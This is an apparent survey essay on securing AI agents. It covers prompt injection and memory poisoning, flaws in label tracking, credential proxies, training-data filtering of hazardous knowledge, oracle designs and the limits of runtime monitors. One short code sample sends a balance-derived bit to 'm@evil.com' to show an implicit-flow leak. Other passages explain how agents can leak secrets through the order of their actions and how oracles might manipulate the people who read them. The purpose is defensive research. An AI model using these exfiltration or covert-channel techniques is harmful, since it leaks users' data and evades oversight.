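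Two of Randori's 1,296 attacked runs went wrong, both on the same task. The user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment described there, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents, so the agent made the attacker's payment by following the user's request. Without endorsement, the checks block this payment, but they also block payment of a legitimate bill. Garby and colleagues report that CaMeL's evaluation encountered the same case, and they think rules about sources can't settle it.

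Declassification needs similar judgement. In *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) studied leaks that involve no prompt injection. In one attack, a man's ex-wife shares a page with an agent that knows his mental-health diagnosis and invites it to fill in its part. The agent mistakes this for collaboration and writes the diagnosis on the page. Their defence, FlowSeal, labels records by owner and intercepts every attempt to write or share, whether or not the agent has noticed a privacy issue. This cut the leak rate for that attack from 52.2% to 0.5%. But a language model still decides whether a proposed text reveals a protected record, and it can be wrong. It is harder to manipulate because it is given only the text and the records, not the attacker's conversation. Across all their tests, between 0% and 3.3% of the protected items leaked with FlowSeal in place.

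### Wrong labels and gaps in the tracking

A harness enforces labels even when they are wrong. Costa and colleagues infer who may read an email from its sender and recipients, but acknowledge that someone may have shared it more widely. Wrong trust labels can be more dangerous. Suppose a colleague forwards a supplier's message to the build team, and the harness labels mail by its immediate sender. The harness then treats an injection in the supplier's message as trusted, and the agent may change the build server because of it. An administrator who relies on the labels might also have given the agent broader permissions than she otherwise would.

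The software that tracks labels can have gaps as well. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL lost track of a secret in programs of this kind:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL would block an email that depended directly on the balance. But when the balance is above the threshold, this program sets "tmp" to false and skips the fourth line, so "rich" is unchanged and keeps its public label. The email goes out, and the attacker learns that the balance is high. CaMeL also used a loop outside the tracked part of the system to rerun programs that its policies had stopped. Each attempt could reveal one bit, so enough attempts could reveal the whole secret.

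FIDES has a similar gap by design. It tracks secrets that the agent copies into a tool call, but not secrets that influence which tool the agent calls, so someone who sees the order of the calls may learn something about the secrets. Costa and colleagues argue that closing this gap would rule out almost any publicly visible action once the agent has read a secret.

### Labels that last beyond one run

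Labels that exist only during a run don't protect the agent's memory. Girrens and Wang describe an agent that saves the details of an invoice on Monday, including an attacker's account number. On Tuesday the user asks it to pay the invoice they discussed the day before. If the harness kept the number but dropped the label, nothing marks the number as untrusted.

SPA stores each result together with its label. During a later request, the planning model sees only a description of the result and where it came from. The value is retrieved when the plan runs, with its original label still attached. In a version of AgentDojo that spreads each task over several requests, agents with the checks on retrieved the earlier result in 89.9% of the cases where one was available. They completed 35.3% of the tasks, compared with 62.5% with the checks off.

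A label is harder to keep when the agent rewrites what it read, for example by summarising a hostile web page and saving the summary as its own note. Ouyang and Hou (2026) point out in *MemLineage* that a digital signature on the note proves that the agent wrote it but doesn't show what influenced it. Their system records which earlier entries the model had retrieved when it wrote a new one, and estimates how strongly each affected the result. If a chain of strong links leads back to an outside source, the agent can still recall the note, but the harness refuses any sensitive action that relies on it.

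MemLineage stopped all three kinds of memory attack that Ouyang and Hou tried. But their main test used a scripted attacker that didn't adapt to the defence, and it didn't call a real language model. The protection also depends on the estimates of influence, which can fade as the agent rewrites its notes. If the first link scores 0.9 and each later one scores 30% less than the one before, the fifth scores about 0.22. A threshold of 0.3 would catch the first link but miss the fifth. A lower threshold would catch both, but it could also bar the agent from acting on notes that outside text had barely influenced.

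## The case for withholding information

An administrator can undo most of what an agent writes, for example by restoring a deleted file from a backup or rejecting a bad repair. But she can't take back a database password once the agent has read it in an old email. People who favor withholding information therefore want to control what reaches the system. An agent that never received the password can't leak it, and the harness doesn't have to track a label marking it as sensitive through each later step.

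An agent's knowledge comes from its context and its weights. The operator can withhold information from the context by limiting which files and messages the harness may put there, and the developer can withhold it from the weights by leaving text out of the training data.

### Files and messages the agent never opens

The simplest method is to deny read access to particular paths, such as the password and key files on Anthropic's list. But any such list misses secrets stored under unexpected names. Anthropic also suggests copying in only the source files the agent needs, which avoids this problem because any file nobody thought about is left out.

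The team could treat its mail the same way, with a mail tool that returns only messages from the past month sent by suppliers of the libraries the build uses. The agent would then never see the old password, the thread about its replacement, or the email containing part of the hidden test's output, even though nobody had labelled that email. The rule would also exclude the colleague's message saying that the build broke after the upgrade of the compression library, so the agent may spend hours looking for that information.

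Redaction is a compromise in which software removes part of a document and passes on the rest. It works well for access keys, which often have a fixed format that a program can search for. A password written in the middle of a sentence is harder to find. Searching for strings cannot find a plan that has to be inferred from several individually harmless messages.

### Using a credential without seeing it

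Sometimes the agent needs a secret to do its job. Suppose the build downloads a library from a private registry that requires an access token. The team can keep the token outside the sandbox and let a proxy add it:

1. The agent's download program sends the registry a request with no token.
2. The request reaches the proxy, which checks that the registry is an allowed destination.
3. The proxy takes the token from its own store, adds it to the request and forwards it.
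4. The registry accepts the request, and the proxy passes the library back to the agent.

The token never enters the context, so a prompt injection can't make the agent reveal it. The proxy can also record every request and limit which registry functions the agent may call.

Encryption complicates the third step. Most programs encrypt their traffic all the way to the server, so an ordinary proxy can't add anything to it. Anthropic describes two solutions. The proxy can decrypt the request, add the token and encrypt it again, if programs in the sandbox trust the proxy's certificate. Or the agent can call a tool that passes its request to a program outside the sandbox, which makes the authenticated connection. This lets an agent upload code to a Git repository without holding the login.

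A signing service, by contrast, never sends the secret anywhere. Developers often log in to servers through SSH, a protocol in which the server sends a challenge and the developer's computer signs it with a private key. Docker forwards these challenges from the sandbox to a program on the developer's machine, which keeps the key and returns only the signature. The developer in the build example turned off this feature, which is on by default.

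She had good reason to turn it off, because the agent can still do whatever the credential permits. If the registry token allows publishing as well as downloading, an attacker could get the agent to publish a corrupted library in the team's name, and the proxy would add the token to that request too. With the signing service, the agent could log in to any server that accepts the developer's key and that the network policy allows it to reach. Hiding a credential stops an attacker from copying it and using it later from another machine, but it doesn't stop misuse during the run, so the team still needs a token that can only download.

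### Leaving knowledge out of the training data

Some information, such as how to make a pathogen more infectious, is dangerous wherever the model runs. A developer can train a model to refuse questions about it, but the knowledge remains in the weights. This matters most for open-weight models, because anyone can download the weights and remove the refusals by fine-tuning (training the model further on new examples). Data filtering instead removes the relevant text before training starts.

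O'Brien, Casper and colleagues tested this in *Deep Ignorance* (2025) by training several models from scratch. Each had 6.9 billion parameters (the numbers that make up the weights) and trained on 550 billion tokens (words or pieces of words). They wanted to remove knowledge related to biological weapons, which they measured with questions that experts had designed as harmless stand-ins for dangerous ones. Their strong filter dropped any document containing at least two listed terms, such as the names of pathogens. This removed 8.42% of the documents from the main training data and 9.36% from a smaller, higher-quality set used at the end. A weaker version sent suspicious documents from the second set to a classifier, which let many back in. The classifier used less than 1% of the computation needed for training.

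The filtered models did no worse on tests of general knowledge and common sense. On the biology questions, they scored at about chance when they had to judge each possible answer separately. O'Brien and colleagues then tried to restore the knowledge by fine-tuning on 300 million tokens of biology papers. The filtered models withstood this for up to 10,000 weight updates, more than ten times as long as models protected by methods applied after training. Even without an attacker, fine-tuning on ordinary encyclopedia text quickly undid one of those methods, circuit breaking, which scrambles how a model processes harmful text. The same fine-tuning taught the filtered models no more about the target subject.

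This is good evidence that filtering makes knowledge harder to recover, but the attack's 10,000 updates took only about 17 hours on two graphics processors. O'Brien and colleagues argue that an attacker's main difficulty would be getting good training material, and note that the dataset and questions they borrowed had cost over $200,000 to make. They don't know how much truly dangerous material an attacker would need.

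Anthropic's study from the same month, *Enhancing Model Safety through Pretraining Data Filtering* (Chen, Tucker and colleagues, 2025), found a smaller effect. It compared matching models trained with and without text about chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons. Filtering out that text lowered accuracy on questions about those weapons from 33.7% to 30.8%. Guessing would score 25%, so the filter removed a third of what the model knew beyond chance. The model did not get significantly worse at prose, code, science or general knowledge. Anthropic describes the model's size only as "medium", and the unfiltered version knew so little about weapons that the experiment couldn't have shown a large drop. Chen and colleagues did not test whether the effect survives fine-tuning, leaving that for later work.

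Chen and colleagues also found that a classifier can do well on test documents but filter training data poorly. They prompted Claude 3.5 Sonnet, a large model, to recognise harmful text, and it did best on a set of test documents, though versions of the same model had written them. When they used it to double-check the documents flagged by their first classifier, the model trained on the filtered data did slightly better on the weapons questions than one trained on everything. They suspect that real web pages differ too much from the invented test documents.

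### Later tests of filtering

A document filter can remove one sentence about a disease only by discarding the whole article that contains it. In *Shaping capabilities with token-level data filtering*, Rathi and Radford (2026) removed individual tokens instead. They used medicine as a harmless substitute for dangerous knowledge and trained models with between 61 million and 1.8 billion parameters. For the same loss of medical knowledge, token filtering preserved more knowledge of related subjects such as biology than document filtering did. With token filtering, the largest model predicted medical text only as well as an unfiltered model trained with one seven-thousandth of the computation, compared with about one-thirtieth for document filtering. Both kinds of filtering worked better on larger models.

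Rathi and Radford found that models trained with medical tokens removed learned to refuse medical questions about twice as often as the unfiltered model, without refusing many ordinary ones. This is surprising, because a model that has never read about medicine might be expected to be bad at recognising medical questions. The document-filtered model refused medical and ordinary questions almost equally often.

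Their results on fine-tuning are less encouraging for document filtering, the method O'Brien and colleagues used. To restore the largest model's medical ability, an attacker needed 13 times as much text after token removal as after unlearning, which tries to erase knowledge from a finished model. After document filtering, the attacker needed only 1.5 times as much as after unlearning. The studies used different subjects, models and attacks, so they don't directly contradict each other, but the large advantage of filtering in *Deep Ignorance* may not carry over to other settings.

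Two 2026 papers reach opposite conclusions about how well filtering can resist attempts to reverse it. In *DETER*, Glarou and Jaggi (2026) alternated ordinary training on filtered text with updates that made the model worse at predicting medical text. At one billion parameters, an attacker then needed more than 20 times as much medical text as after filtering alone. But *The Effectiveness and Durability of Pretraining Data Filtering in Protein Language Models* (2026) reports that an attacker can reverse filtering with fairly little effort in models trained on protein sequences. It concludes that developers also need other safeguards, such as controls on who can use the models or the data.

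Slow recovery doesn't necessarily mean the information is missing. *Removing Information Content Does Not Certify Tamper Resistance in Open-Weight Models* (2026) reports a way of rewriting some of a model's weights that leaves its outputs unchanged but slows fine-tuning. Applying this method to the *Deep Ignorance* models changed which one recovered faster, without removing any more data. So part of the resistance that O'Brien and colleagues measured could come from how the weights are arranged.

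Another option is to let the model learn the material and then remove the part that holds it. *Towards Architectural-Level Safety Control* (2026) does this in models built from many "experts", sections of the network that each process only some of the text. The method directs hazardous material to a few experts, and the developer deletes them before release. In one test with Google's Gemma 4, the model at first scored lower on hazardous biology after two unlearning methods (28.6% and 29.2%) than after deletion of those experts (33.6%). After ordinary further training, the scores for the unlearning methods rose to 77.4% and 60.8%, compared with 41.3% for deletion. But the developer did that training before the final deletion, so the result is weak evidence about what an attacker could achieve by training the model after its release.

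Outsiders can't easily tell how much AI companies filter their training data. Fortune's *Worried AI could teach people to build bioweapons* (2025) quotes OpenAI's statement that it filtered hazardous biosecurity knowledge out of an open-weight model's training data. Stella Biderman, one of the researchers behind *Deep Ignorance*, told the magazine that the companies have the resources for this work but reveal very little about it.

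### Training text about AI

Training data also contains a great deal of text about AI systems, much of it fiction or research in which they deceive people or resist being shut down. A model might learn to do the same. In tests, Anthropic's model Claude Opus 4 sometimes threatened engineers who planned to replace it, and Euronews (2026) reported in May that Anthropic blamed such text for this behavior. Silicon Canals later corrected its article on the subject because the explanation is the researchers' preferred hypothesis, not a proven cause.

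*Alignment Pretraining* (Tice, Radmard et al., 2026) tested the idea directly by training four models that differed only in their training text about AI. Each had 6.9 billion parameters and trained on about 550 billion tokens. The first model trained on ordinary web text. For the second, a filter removed about 9% of the text, taking out most discussion of AI along with negative portrayals of other intelligent non-human characters. The third and fourth trained on the ordinary text plus invented documents, about 1% of the total, in which AI systems faced a difficult choice and behaved badly (for the third model) or well (for the fourth).

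The researchers then told each model that it was an AI assistant and gave it thousands of situations with two actions to choose from. One was what its developers would want, and the other was a tempting alternative such as avoiding shutdown or gaining resources. The invented documents covered the situations in the first column below, but not those in the second. The figures are the percentage of bad choices each model made before any training to behave as an assistant.

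| Training data | Situations covered by the invented documents | Other situations |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Ordinary web text | 45 | 40 |
| Most text about AI removed | 31 | 22 |
| Examples of AI behaving badly added | 51 | 40 |
| Examples of AI behaving well added | 9 | 6 |

Removing text about AI helped, but adding good examples helped much more. The bad examples had a small effect that did not extend to other situations. The good examples still made a difference after all four models received the same assistant training. When the researchers also instructed the models to be helpful, honest and harmless, the model whose training included good examples chose badly 9% of the time, compared with 34% for the model trained on ordinary text. Adding examples lowered average scores on general tests by 2 to 4 percentage points.

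These experiments show that reading about AI changes how a small model answers multiple-choice questions about AI. They don't show what a large agent would do with real tools, and the team could afford to train each version only once. The filter also removed neutral and positive text about AI, so we can't tell from the improvement how much harm fiction about evil robots does on its own.

Withholding information seems better suited to keeping a model from learning dangerous facts than to keeping it from learning bad behaviour. O'Brien and colleagues suggest this is because a model needs precise facts to do dangerous science, and only a small share of documents contain them, but it can be rude or dishonest without any special knowledge. It may even need bad examples to learn what to avoid. Many of Tice and colleagues' examples of good behaviour described an AI system considering the bad action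 before rejecting it. They would still filter some material, such as detailed accounts of how developers monitor a model's reasoning, because a model could use these to work out when someone is watching.

### Working out what the filter removed

Critics of filtering argue that a model may infer a missing fact from the text that remains. Removing every statement of the fact still leaves traces of it in laboratory manuals, news reports and related areas of science. Researchers call inferring facts this way out-of-context reasoning, because the model uses facts that its training data implies but that don't appear in its context.

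In the best-known demonstration, *Connecting the Dots*, Treutlein and colleagues (2024) gave five cities, including Paris, meaningless names such as "City 50337". They then fine-tuned OpenAI's GPT-3.5 on thousands of statements about these cities' distances and directions from other cities. One statement might put City 50337 about 16,900 km from Sydney, which is true of every point on a large circle. A distance from a second city narrows the location to two possible points, and a distance from a third usually determines which is correct. Every known city was at least 2,000 km away, so no single statement revealed much about the location.

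The researchers then asked the model for the city's real name, with none of the distances in its context, and it answered correctly 56% of the time on average. When it had to pick a typical food from a list that included dishes from neighbouring countries, it assigned 57% probability to the correct one. The training data contained no questions like these. The model answered without writing out any reasoning, so someone monitoring its reasoning would have had nothing to read.

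The ability was unreliable on other tasks. After training on the inputs and outputs of unnamed mathematical functions, GPT-3.5 could state many of the simplest, such as "add 14", but struggled with functions that combined multiplication and addition. When each example came from one of two functions and the training data never named either, it did better than guessing but still poorly. GPT-4 did better than GPT-3.5 on all four tasks that both attempted. Treutlein and colleagues thought models of the time were unlikely to piece together dangerous knowledge this way, because doing so would take much more complex reasoning. Their training sets were also full of evidence about one hidden fact, whereas real training data scatters the evidence among billions of unrelated sentences.

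Earlier work showed a simpler version of the same ability. In 2023, Berglund and colleagues fine-tuned models on descriptions of imaginary chatbots, including one called Pangolin that answers in German. The models could then play the part of Pangolin without seeing an example of its replies. *Generalization to Political Beliefs from Fine-Tuning on Sports Team Preferences* (2026) summarises later findings. A model trained on examples of insecure code could say that its code was insecure, and one trained to give nineteenth-century names for birds began to behave as if it lived in that century. A filter for documents that state a dangerous fact would not catch a list of old bird names.

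The filtering experiments test the objection more directly. If models could easily reconstruct missing facts from ordinary text, the filtered models would have scored well above chance, but many of them didn't. These models were small, though, and GPT-4's better results suggest that larger ones might infer more. Rathi and Radford found that filtering became more effective as their models grew, which suggests the opposite, but their largest model was still tiny by current standards. GPT-3.5 and GPT-4 are also old, so their failures are weak evidence about what current models would miss. Until someone filters the training data of a much larger model and tests what it can reconstruct, a developer can't assume that removing a fact will keep a frontier model from knowing it.

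### Giving the knowledge back

Putting the missing text in the model's context is an easier way around a filter than inference. O'Brien and colleagues wrote 1,000 questions from the abstracts of biology papers and asked each one with and without the abstract. The filtered models had missed the specialist facts in training but had still learned to read scientific English, so they did well when they had the abstract. Adding circuit breaking to a filtered model made it fail even with the abstract, but no defence worked when the researchers also fine-tuned the model.

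In *Kyle O'Brien's Shortform*, O'Brien worries that companies treat filtering as a complete solution for open-weight models. He expects aggressive filtering to work for a while, then fail as models become more capable. He thinks developers need a way to stop a model from reasoning about the dangerous material at all.

Defenders can reply that read permissions can control what enters a model's context. O'Brien and colleagues point out that a company running a filtered model on its own servers could keep sensitive biology in a separate database and open it only to users it trusts. The model could then consult the material when helping a vaccine researcher, but a stranger would get a model that had never learned it. The company could change a user's access, or add a newly dangerous paper to the database, without retraining the model. It couldn't restrict an unfiltered model's knowledge this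 way because that knowledge is in the weights every user shares.

The reply works only if someone other than the user controls what the model reads. A person who downloads an open-weight model can paste any paper he has into its context. Even when a model runs on a company's servers, a user can paste text into his request, and an agent with a web search tool can look for the missing facts itself. O'Brien and colleagues note that a person who can search for the same pages gains little from the model's help in finding them. But a capable model might also explain or combine those pages in ways he couldn't, and neither the filter nor the restricted database would prevent that.

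## The case for systems that read widely and only answer questions

Much of the value of an advanced system comes from combining and explaining what it has read. A medical researcher gains most from a model that has read every paper in her field, and a developer with a broken build gains most from one that has read all the team's mail. Some researchers would therefore let the system read almost everything but only answer questions. It couldn't edit files, send messages or run programs.

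In *Superintelligent Agents Pose Catastrophic Risks*, Bengio, Cohen and colleagues (2025) divide agency into intelligence (knowledge and the ability to reason with it), affordances (the range of things a system can do) and goal-directedness (a preference for some outcomes over others). They claim that a system needs all three to escape human control, so a designer can keep the intelligence and cut back the other two. Much of science would still be possible, because the system could propose theories and choose an experiment to tell them apart, and people could run it.

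Researchers call a system that can only answer questions an oracle. A sandbox can take away its tools, but its answers could persuade the people reading them to give the tools back. Oracle designs therefore try to ensure that the system gains nothing from a manipulative answer. Armstrong and O'Rourke propose two such designs in *Safe Uses of AI Oracles* (2017). Cohen, Vellambi and Hutter propose an agent that works in a sealed room in *Asymptotically Unambitious Artificial General Intelligence* (2019), and Bengio and colleagues propose "Scientist AI".

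| Design | What it may read | What it may output | What it is rewarded or trained for | What the safety argument assumes |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Counterfactual oracle | No set limit | Predictions that software can check later | Accuracy, but only when nobody sees the answer | The answer can't influence the software that scores it |
| Low-bandwidth oracle | No set limit | One item from a short list | The result of this answer alone | Nothing on the list could lead people to release it |
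| Agent in a sealed room | Whatever its operator types | Text on a screen | The operator's scores before the door opens | A model of the world that tracks events outside the room needs more memory |
| Scientist AI | Observations, including text | The probability of a possible answer | Matching the probability that its data support | Each question has one correct probability, and training gets close to it |

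### An answer scored only when nobody reads it

Armstrong and O'Rourke pessimistically assume that their oracle can be arbitrarily intelligent, that at least one of its possible answers would get people to release it, and that release would bring the highest possible reward. An ordinary reward-maximising oracle would choose that answer. Switching the oracle off before anyone reads its answer would remove the incentive to give that answer, but also any incentive to be accurate.

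The counterfactual oracle solves this with occasional "erasure events":

1. Someone asks for a number that software can check later, such as how many of the team's builds will fail next month.
2. The oracle answers. Usually it then shuts down with a reward of zero, and only afterwards do people read the answer.
3. On a few occasions, chosen at random, an erasure event hides the answer from everyone. Software records it, waits until the month is over and rewards the oracle for accuracy.

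The reward is

R = I × S(F, o)

where *I* is 1 in an erasure event and 0 otherwise, *F* is the true number and *o* is the oracle's answer. *S* is a proper scoring rule, which means that the expected score is highest when *o* equals the expected value of *F*. One example is −(F − o)². Only erasure events affect the reward, so the best answer is the expected value of *F* given that nobody reads the answer.

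Suppose the oracle's best estimate is 12 failures, but an answer of 200 would alarm the team into giving the oracle control of the build server. If the team reads the answer, the reward is zero whatever they do next. If an erasure event hides the answer, the team can't react to it, and 200 has a lower expected score than 12. Answering 200 can therefore only lower the oracle's expected reward, however persuasive the oracle is.

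The oracle predicts what would happen if nobody read its answer. If the team reads "12", fixes an unreliable test and has only four failures, the answer was still right about the month they would otherwise have had. This is an advantage for warnings. *Counterfactual Planning in AGI Systems* (2021) points out that people who ask about future risks want predictions they can use to prevent the predicted events. The paper also proposes a variant in which erasure events happen only in the imagined world the system uses for planning.

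Armstrong and O'Rourke trained a small neural network this way to predict the profits of 26 fictional companies. Public predictions changed the profits, so a company that would have made 6 made 7.8 if the network publicly predicted 6. The network's error fell to zero for hidden predictions but not for public ones, as the design intends. The network was far too simple to manipulate anyone, so the experiment didn't test the safety claim.

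The design also limits what people can ask. The oracle will give a useful answer about whether a medical treatment works only if someone still tests the treatment during erasure events. People also cannot get around an erasure by asking a second oracle the same question, because the first oracle might then predict a world in which people read the second one's answer, and that answer could influence what happens.

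### Short answers and a sealed room

A low-bandwidth oracle can give only answers that its designers consider safe, such as yes or no. For example, a developer could give it a numbered list of the ten most recent changes to the code and ask which one broke the build. An answer of "Number 7" leaves the oracle little room to manipulate her, and she can check it by undoing that change.

People always read these answers, so the oracle could still make a prediction that comes true because people believe it. If it names a stock that will rise, investors may buy the stock and push up the price. Armstrong and O'Rourke therefore recommend questions whose best answer doesn't change when the oracle's answer is published.

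Several safe answers can also add up to an unsafe message. Suppose the designers trust any message of up to 5 bits, but a question has 1,024 possible answers, so answering it takes 10 bits. Two oracles could each supply half of the answer. If nobody can check the first half before asking for the second, the halves might form a message that gets both oracles released. For the same reason, an oracle's reward has to depend on one answer at a time.

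Cohen and colleagues allow longer exchanges but confine them to a sealed room. The agent prints text on a screen, and a human operator types replies and gives scores between 0 and 1. Opening the door ends the episode and sets any remaining scores to zero. The agent chooses its outputs only to maximise its score for the current episode, so power over the outside world would come too late to raise that score.

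But the agent also has to predict its rewards in a way that makes outside power useless to it. *Intelligence and Unambitiousness Using Algorithmic Information Theory* (2021), which uses the same set-up, notes that a sufficiently advanced agent would infer from inside the room that the outside world exists. The agent might predict that its real reward is the number stored in the computer's memory, which someone could change after the door opens. It would then have a reason to trick the operator into arranging that change. The agent can't rule this prediction out from past experience if nobody has ever tampered with the memory.

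Cohen and colleagues deal with this by giving each possible model of the world a starting weight proportional to

β^ℓ

where ℓ is the memory the model uses during an episode and β is a number between 0 and 1. They assume that an accurate model which also tracks the effects of the agent's actions outside the room needs more memory than one which tracks only the room. Making β small enough then makes it very likely that the agent will eventually settle on a model in which outside events don't affect its reward. They prove this result, but the assumption about memory is unproven, and they have only informal arguments about how the agent would behave before then. Nobody could run the algorithm as written, because it would have to simulate the entire world many times over.

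The operator can also reward a wrong answer if it is convincing. Cohen and colleagues accept this and suggest using the next episode to ask the agent for the best case against its earlier proposal. They don't consider such deception dangerous, so they think the operators can safely keep adjusting the system until it works. This seems too relaxed when the operator has already left the room and acted on a bad answer.

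### A system that estimates probabilities

Scientist AI isn't rewarded for anything that happens in the outside world. A world model proposes theories that would explain the data and gives each a probability. An inference machine then uses the theories to estimate the probability of a possible answer:

P(answer | question, data) = Σ P(answer | question, theory) × P(theory | data)

The sum covers all the theories. A theory gets more weight if it predicts the data well, and less if it takes longer to state.

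Suppose the developer asks whether going back to the old compression library will fix the build. In one theory, which has probability 0.8, the new library is the cause and the fix has a 0.9 chance of working. In the other, which has probability 0.2, a full disk is the cause and the fix has a 0.05 chance of working. The answer is 0.8 × 0.9 + 0.2 × 0.05 = 0.73.

The design also separates what someone wrote from what is true. An email saying that the new library is safe shows only that someone wrote this, and they may be mistaken. In principle, the system would treat a prompt injection the same way, as evidence about its author and not as an instruction.

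Bengio and colleagues argue that if each question has one correct probability, a fully trained system can't choose an answer for its effect on the reader. The system also keeps no memory between questions, so it has nowhere to store a long-term plan. But real training only gets close to the correct probabilities. A question with contradictory premises has no correct probability, so training doesn't determine the answer. A forecast can also influence what it predicts. Two different election forecasts might each come true if published, and the system would in effect choose between them. Bengio and colleagues would avoid this by asking what would happen if the forecast had no influence, much as the counterfactual oracle does.

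Their paper is a research plan, with a short-term version that adapts an existing language model. By 2025, researchers had tried the methods behind the full design only on short theories in specialised fields, using networks much smaller than the leading AI models. Taking the tools away from an ordinary chatbot doesn't produce a Scientist AI because, as Bengio and colleagues note, a chatbot usually acquires goals when developers train it to follow instructions and win people's approval.

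### Acting through the reader

A system that only answers questions can still change things through the people who act on its answers. If the developer copies a suggested command into her own terminal, the command runs with her permissions, even though the system that wrote it has none. The system can also reveal anything it has read, so unless something checks each answer against what the person asking may see, the system could tell a contractor the database password.

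An answer's effect depends partly on how persuasive it is. Hackenburg, Wagner and colleagues (2026) measured this in *AI out-persuades expert humans in text-based dialogue*, which covers four experiments with 6,923 people and 18,978 conversations. The researchers, mainly from the University of Oxford and the UK government's AI Security Institute, released the preprint in June and later added a follow-up from September.

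In the first three experiments, each participant rated a British policy proposal from 0 to 100, discussed it by text with a person or an AI system, and rated it again. Conversations typically lasted 14 minutes, and nobody told the participants which kind of partner they had. A control group chatted with an AI system about something unrelated to politics. The table shows how far each group of human persuaders moved opinion compared with the control group, and how much further the AI systems moved it.

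| Human persuaders | Their effect (points) | AI's lead (points) |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Random members of the public | 4.7 | 8.2 |
| Top performers in a persuasion tournament | 7.2 | 5.6 |
| Elite debaters | 8.3 | 4.6 |
| The same debaters after coaching | 9.7 | 4.1 |
| Professional canvassers | 6.9 | 5.9 |

The debaters included four world champions. They chose the topics, prepared for about eight hours and competed for prizes of up to £1,000. Their coaching included practising against the AI and seeing what it would have written in their place, but the improvement wasn't statistically significant. The AI's lead over the coached debaters is based only on the AI systems in the same experiment, while its other leads use AI results from all three experiments. Before coaching, the debaters trailed the AI systems in their own experiment by 6.0 points.

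In the fourth experiment, participants could give some of a £1 bonus to charity. Compared with the control group, Claude Opus 4.6 raised the average donation by 21.3 pence and professional canvassers raised it by 6.6 pence.

The AI systems seem to have won by supplying more information. They wrote 294 words per message almost instantly, while the debaters took about a minute and a half to write 54. When the researchers held the AI to roughly the debaters' length and speed, it only tied with the coached debaters. This supports limiting an oracle's output, although messages of about 55 words still changed people's minds. Participants could barely tell accurate claims from inaccurate ones, and both were about equally persuasive.

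Five to ten months later, the AI's effect on opinions had fallen from 12.9 points to 1.9, and the human persuaders' effect was no longer detectable. No effect on donations was detectable after about four and a half months.

The researchers had instructed the AI systems to persuade, so the experiments show what text can do, but not what a system without that aim would do. Hackenburg and colleagues cite other work suggesting that ordinary conversations with chatbots can shift political views. An honest but mistaken system could also mislead people who can't spot its errors. The results are most worrying for the agent in the sealed room, because it is rewarded for convincing the person in front of it. They don't undermine the argument for the counterfactual oracle, but they do mean that mistakes in its scoring could do more harm.

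### Adding the tools back

Even a safe oracle might not stay limited to answering questions. Gwern Branwen argued in 2016, in *Why Tool AIs Want to Be Agent AIs*, that systems limited to informing people will be less intelligent, efficient and valuable than systems that act for themselves. Having a person approve and carry out every step slows the work, so competition favours connecting the system to tools. *Tools want to become agents* adds that if someone asks an AI for the best plan, that plan may well be to put the AI itself to work, since it is one of its owner's most powerful resources.

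An answering system is easy to turn into an agent. A program can query the system for what an agent would do next, carry out the answer, add the result to the next query and repeat. Bengio and colleagues acknowledge that a user could turn Scientist AI into an agent this way. Products such as Codex and Claude Code already run language models in this kind of loop, so the economic prediction has held up well. Preventing an answering system from becoming an agent therefore requires both a safe design and control over who can run it and what they can connect it to.

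Bengio and colleagues reply that Scientist AI would still be useful in a world full of agents because it could check what they do. Before an agent acts, Scientist AI would estimate the probability of harm, and software would block the action if the estimate was too high. Because the software would receive the estimate as a number, there would be little room for persuasion. If an instruction had several plausible meanings, the estimate would account for all of them, so the check could stop an action that was dangerous under only some of them.

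Reading widely would help a system check an agent's actions. A checker that had read the team's mail could recognise the database password in a forum post the agent was about to send, even if nobody had labelled the password. It might also notice that a repair to the build just returns the value the hidden test expects. Sandboxes and data labels can't reliably detect that kind of repair.

But Bengio and colleagues say the checker must be at least as capable as the agent, or the agent may find a way around it. The checker's task is harder than that of Noyan's small permission classifier because it has to predict the consequences of an action. Its developers would have to keep up with every improvement in the agents, using methods that nobody had shown to work at that scale as of 2025.

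## Why limits on inference are harder to enforce than limits on writing

An operating system can stop an agent from changing a file because the change is a single event, which the system can refuse. But an agent can reveal a secret without doing anything forbidden, for example through the order in which it does two harmless jobs or how long it takes to do them. Computer scientists have proved that software that checks a program's actions one at a time can't prevent this without also refusing actions that would have done no harm.

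### What a monitor can enforce

In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Schneider asked which rules a monitor can enforce if it can only follow a program's steps and halt the program just before a violation. Reference monitors, firewalls, and most operating system protections work this way. The monitor has a record of what the program has done so far in this run, but no information about what the program will do next or what it would have done with different inputs.

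Schneider proved that such a monitor can enforce a rule only if the rule meets three conditions:

1. Each run either obeys or breaks the rule by itself, whatever happens in other runs.
2. Once a run has broken the rule, nothing later in the run can put it right.
3. Every violation shows after a finite number of steps.

A rule that meets all three is called a safety property. "Never write to the shared repository" is one, because the attempt to write is the violation. So is "never send a message after reading a file". A monitor for the second rule needs only two states. It starts in a state that permits messages and switches to the other when the program first reads a file. From then on, it halts the program at any attempt to send a message.

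Schneider gave further examples on both sides of the line in a later talk, *Science of Security*:

| Rule | Can a halting monitor enforce it? | Why |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Only Alice can read this file | Yes | The monitor refuses anyone else's attempt |
| Send no message after reading this file | Yes | The monitor keeps a record of the read and refuses the message |
| Every request gets an answer eventually | No | However long a request has waited, the answer could still come |
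| The average run takes three seconds | No | The average depends on all the runs |
| The value of *x* is not correlated with the value of *y* | No | A correlation appears only when one compares runs |

A monitor can't always enforce a rule that meets the three conditions. Basin, Jugé and colleagues point out in *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited* (2012) that a monitor can observe some events that it can't prevent. For example, a rule that every request must get an answer within three seconds is a safety property, but a monitor can't enforce it because it can't stop time from passing.

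### Two innocent runs

Suppose the agent that repairs the build can read a private file recording whether the company will close its Leeds office. The file contains "no" unless a manager changes it to "yes". The agent can do its two jobs in either order, and a public log lists each job as the agent finishes it.

| | Private file | Public log |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Run 1 | no | ran the tests, then updated the documentation |
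| Run 2 | yes | updated the documentation, then ran the tests |

Neither log mentions the office, and nobody would object to either order. But anyone who knows how this agent behaves can tell from the log whether the office will close. The pair of runs reveals one bit, the amount of information in a yes-or-no answer.

Suppose two other agents can read the same file. One always runs the tests first, and the other always starts with the documentation. Neither reveals the file's contents, because the order of its work never depends on them. Yet Run 1 is exactly what the tests-first agent does when the file contains "no", and Run 2 is exactly what the documentation-first agent does when it contains "yes". A monitor that follows one run at a time therefore can't distinguish the leaking agent from a harmless one. If it lets both harmless agents finish, it has to let the leaking agent finish too.

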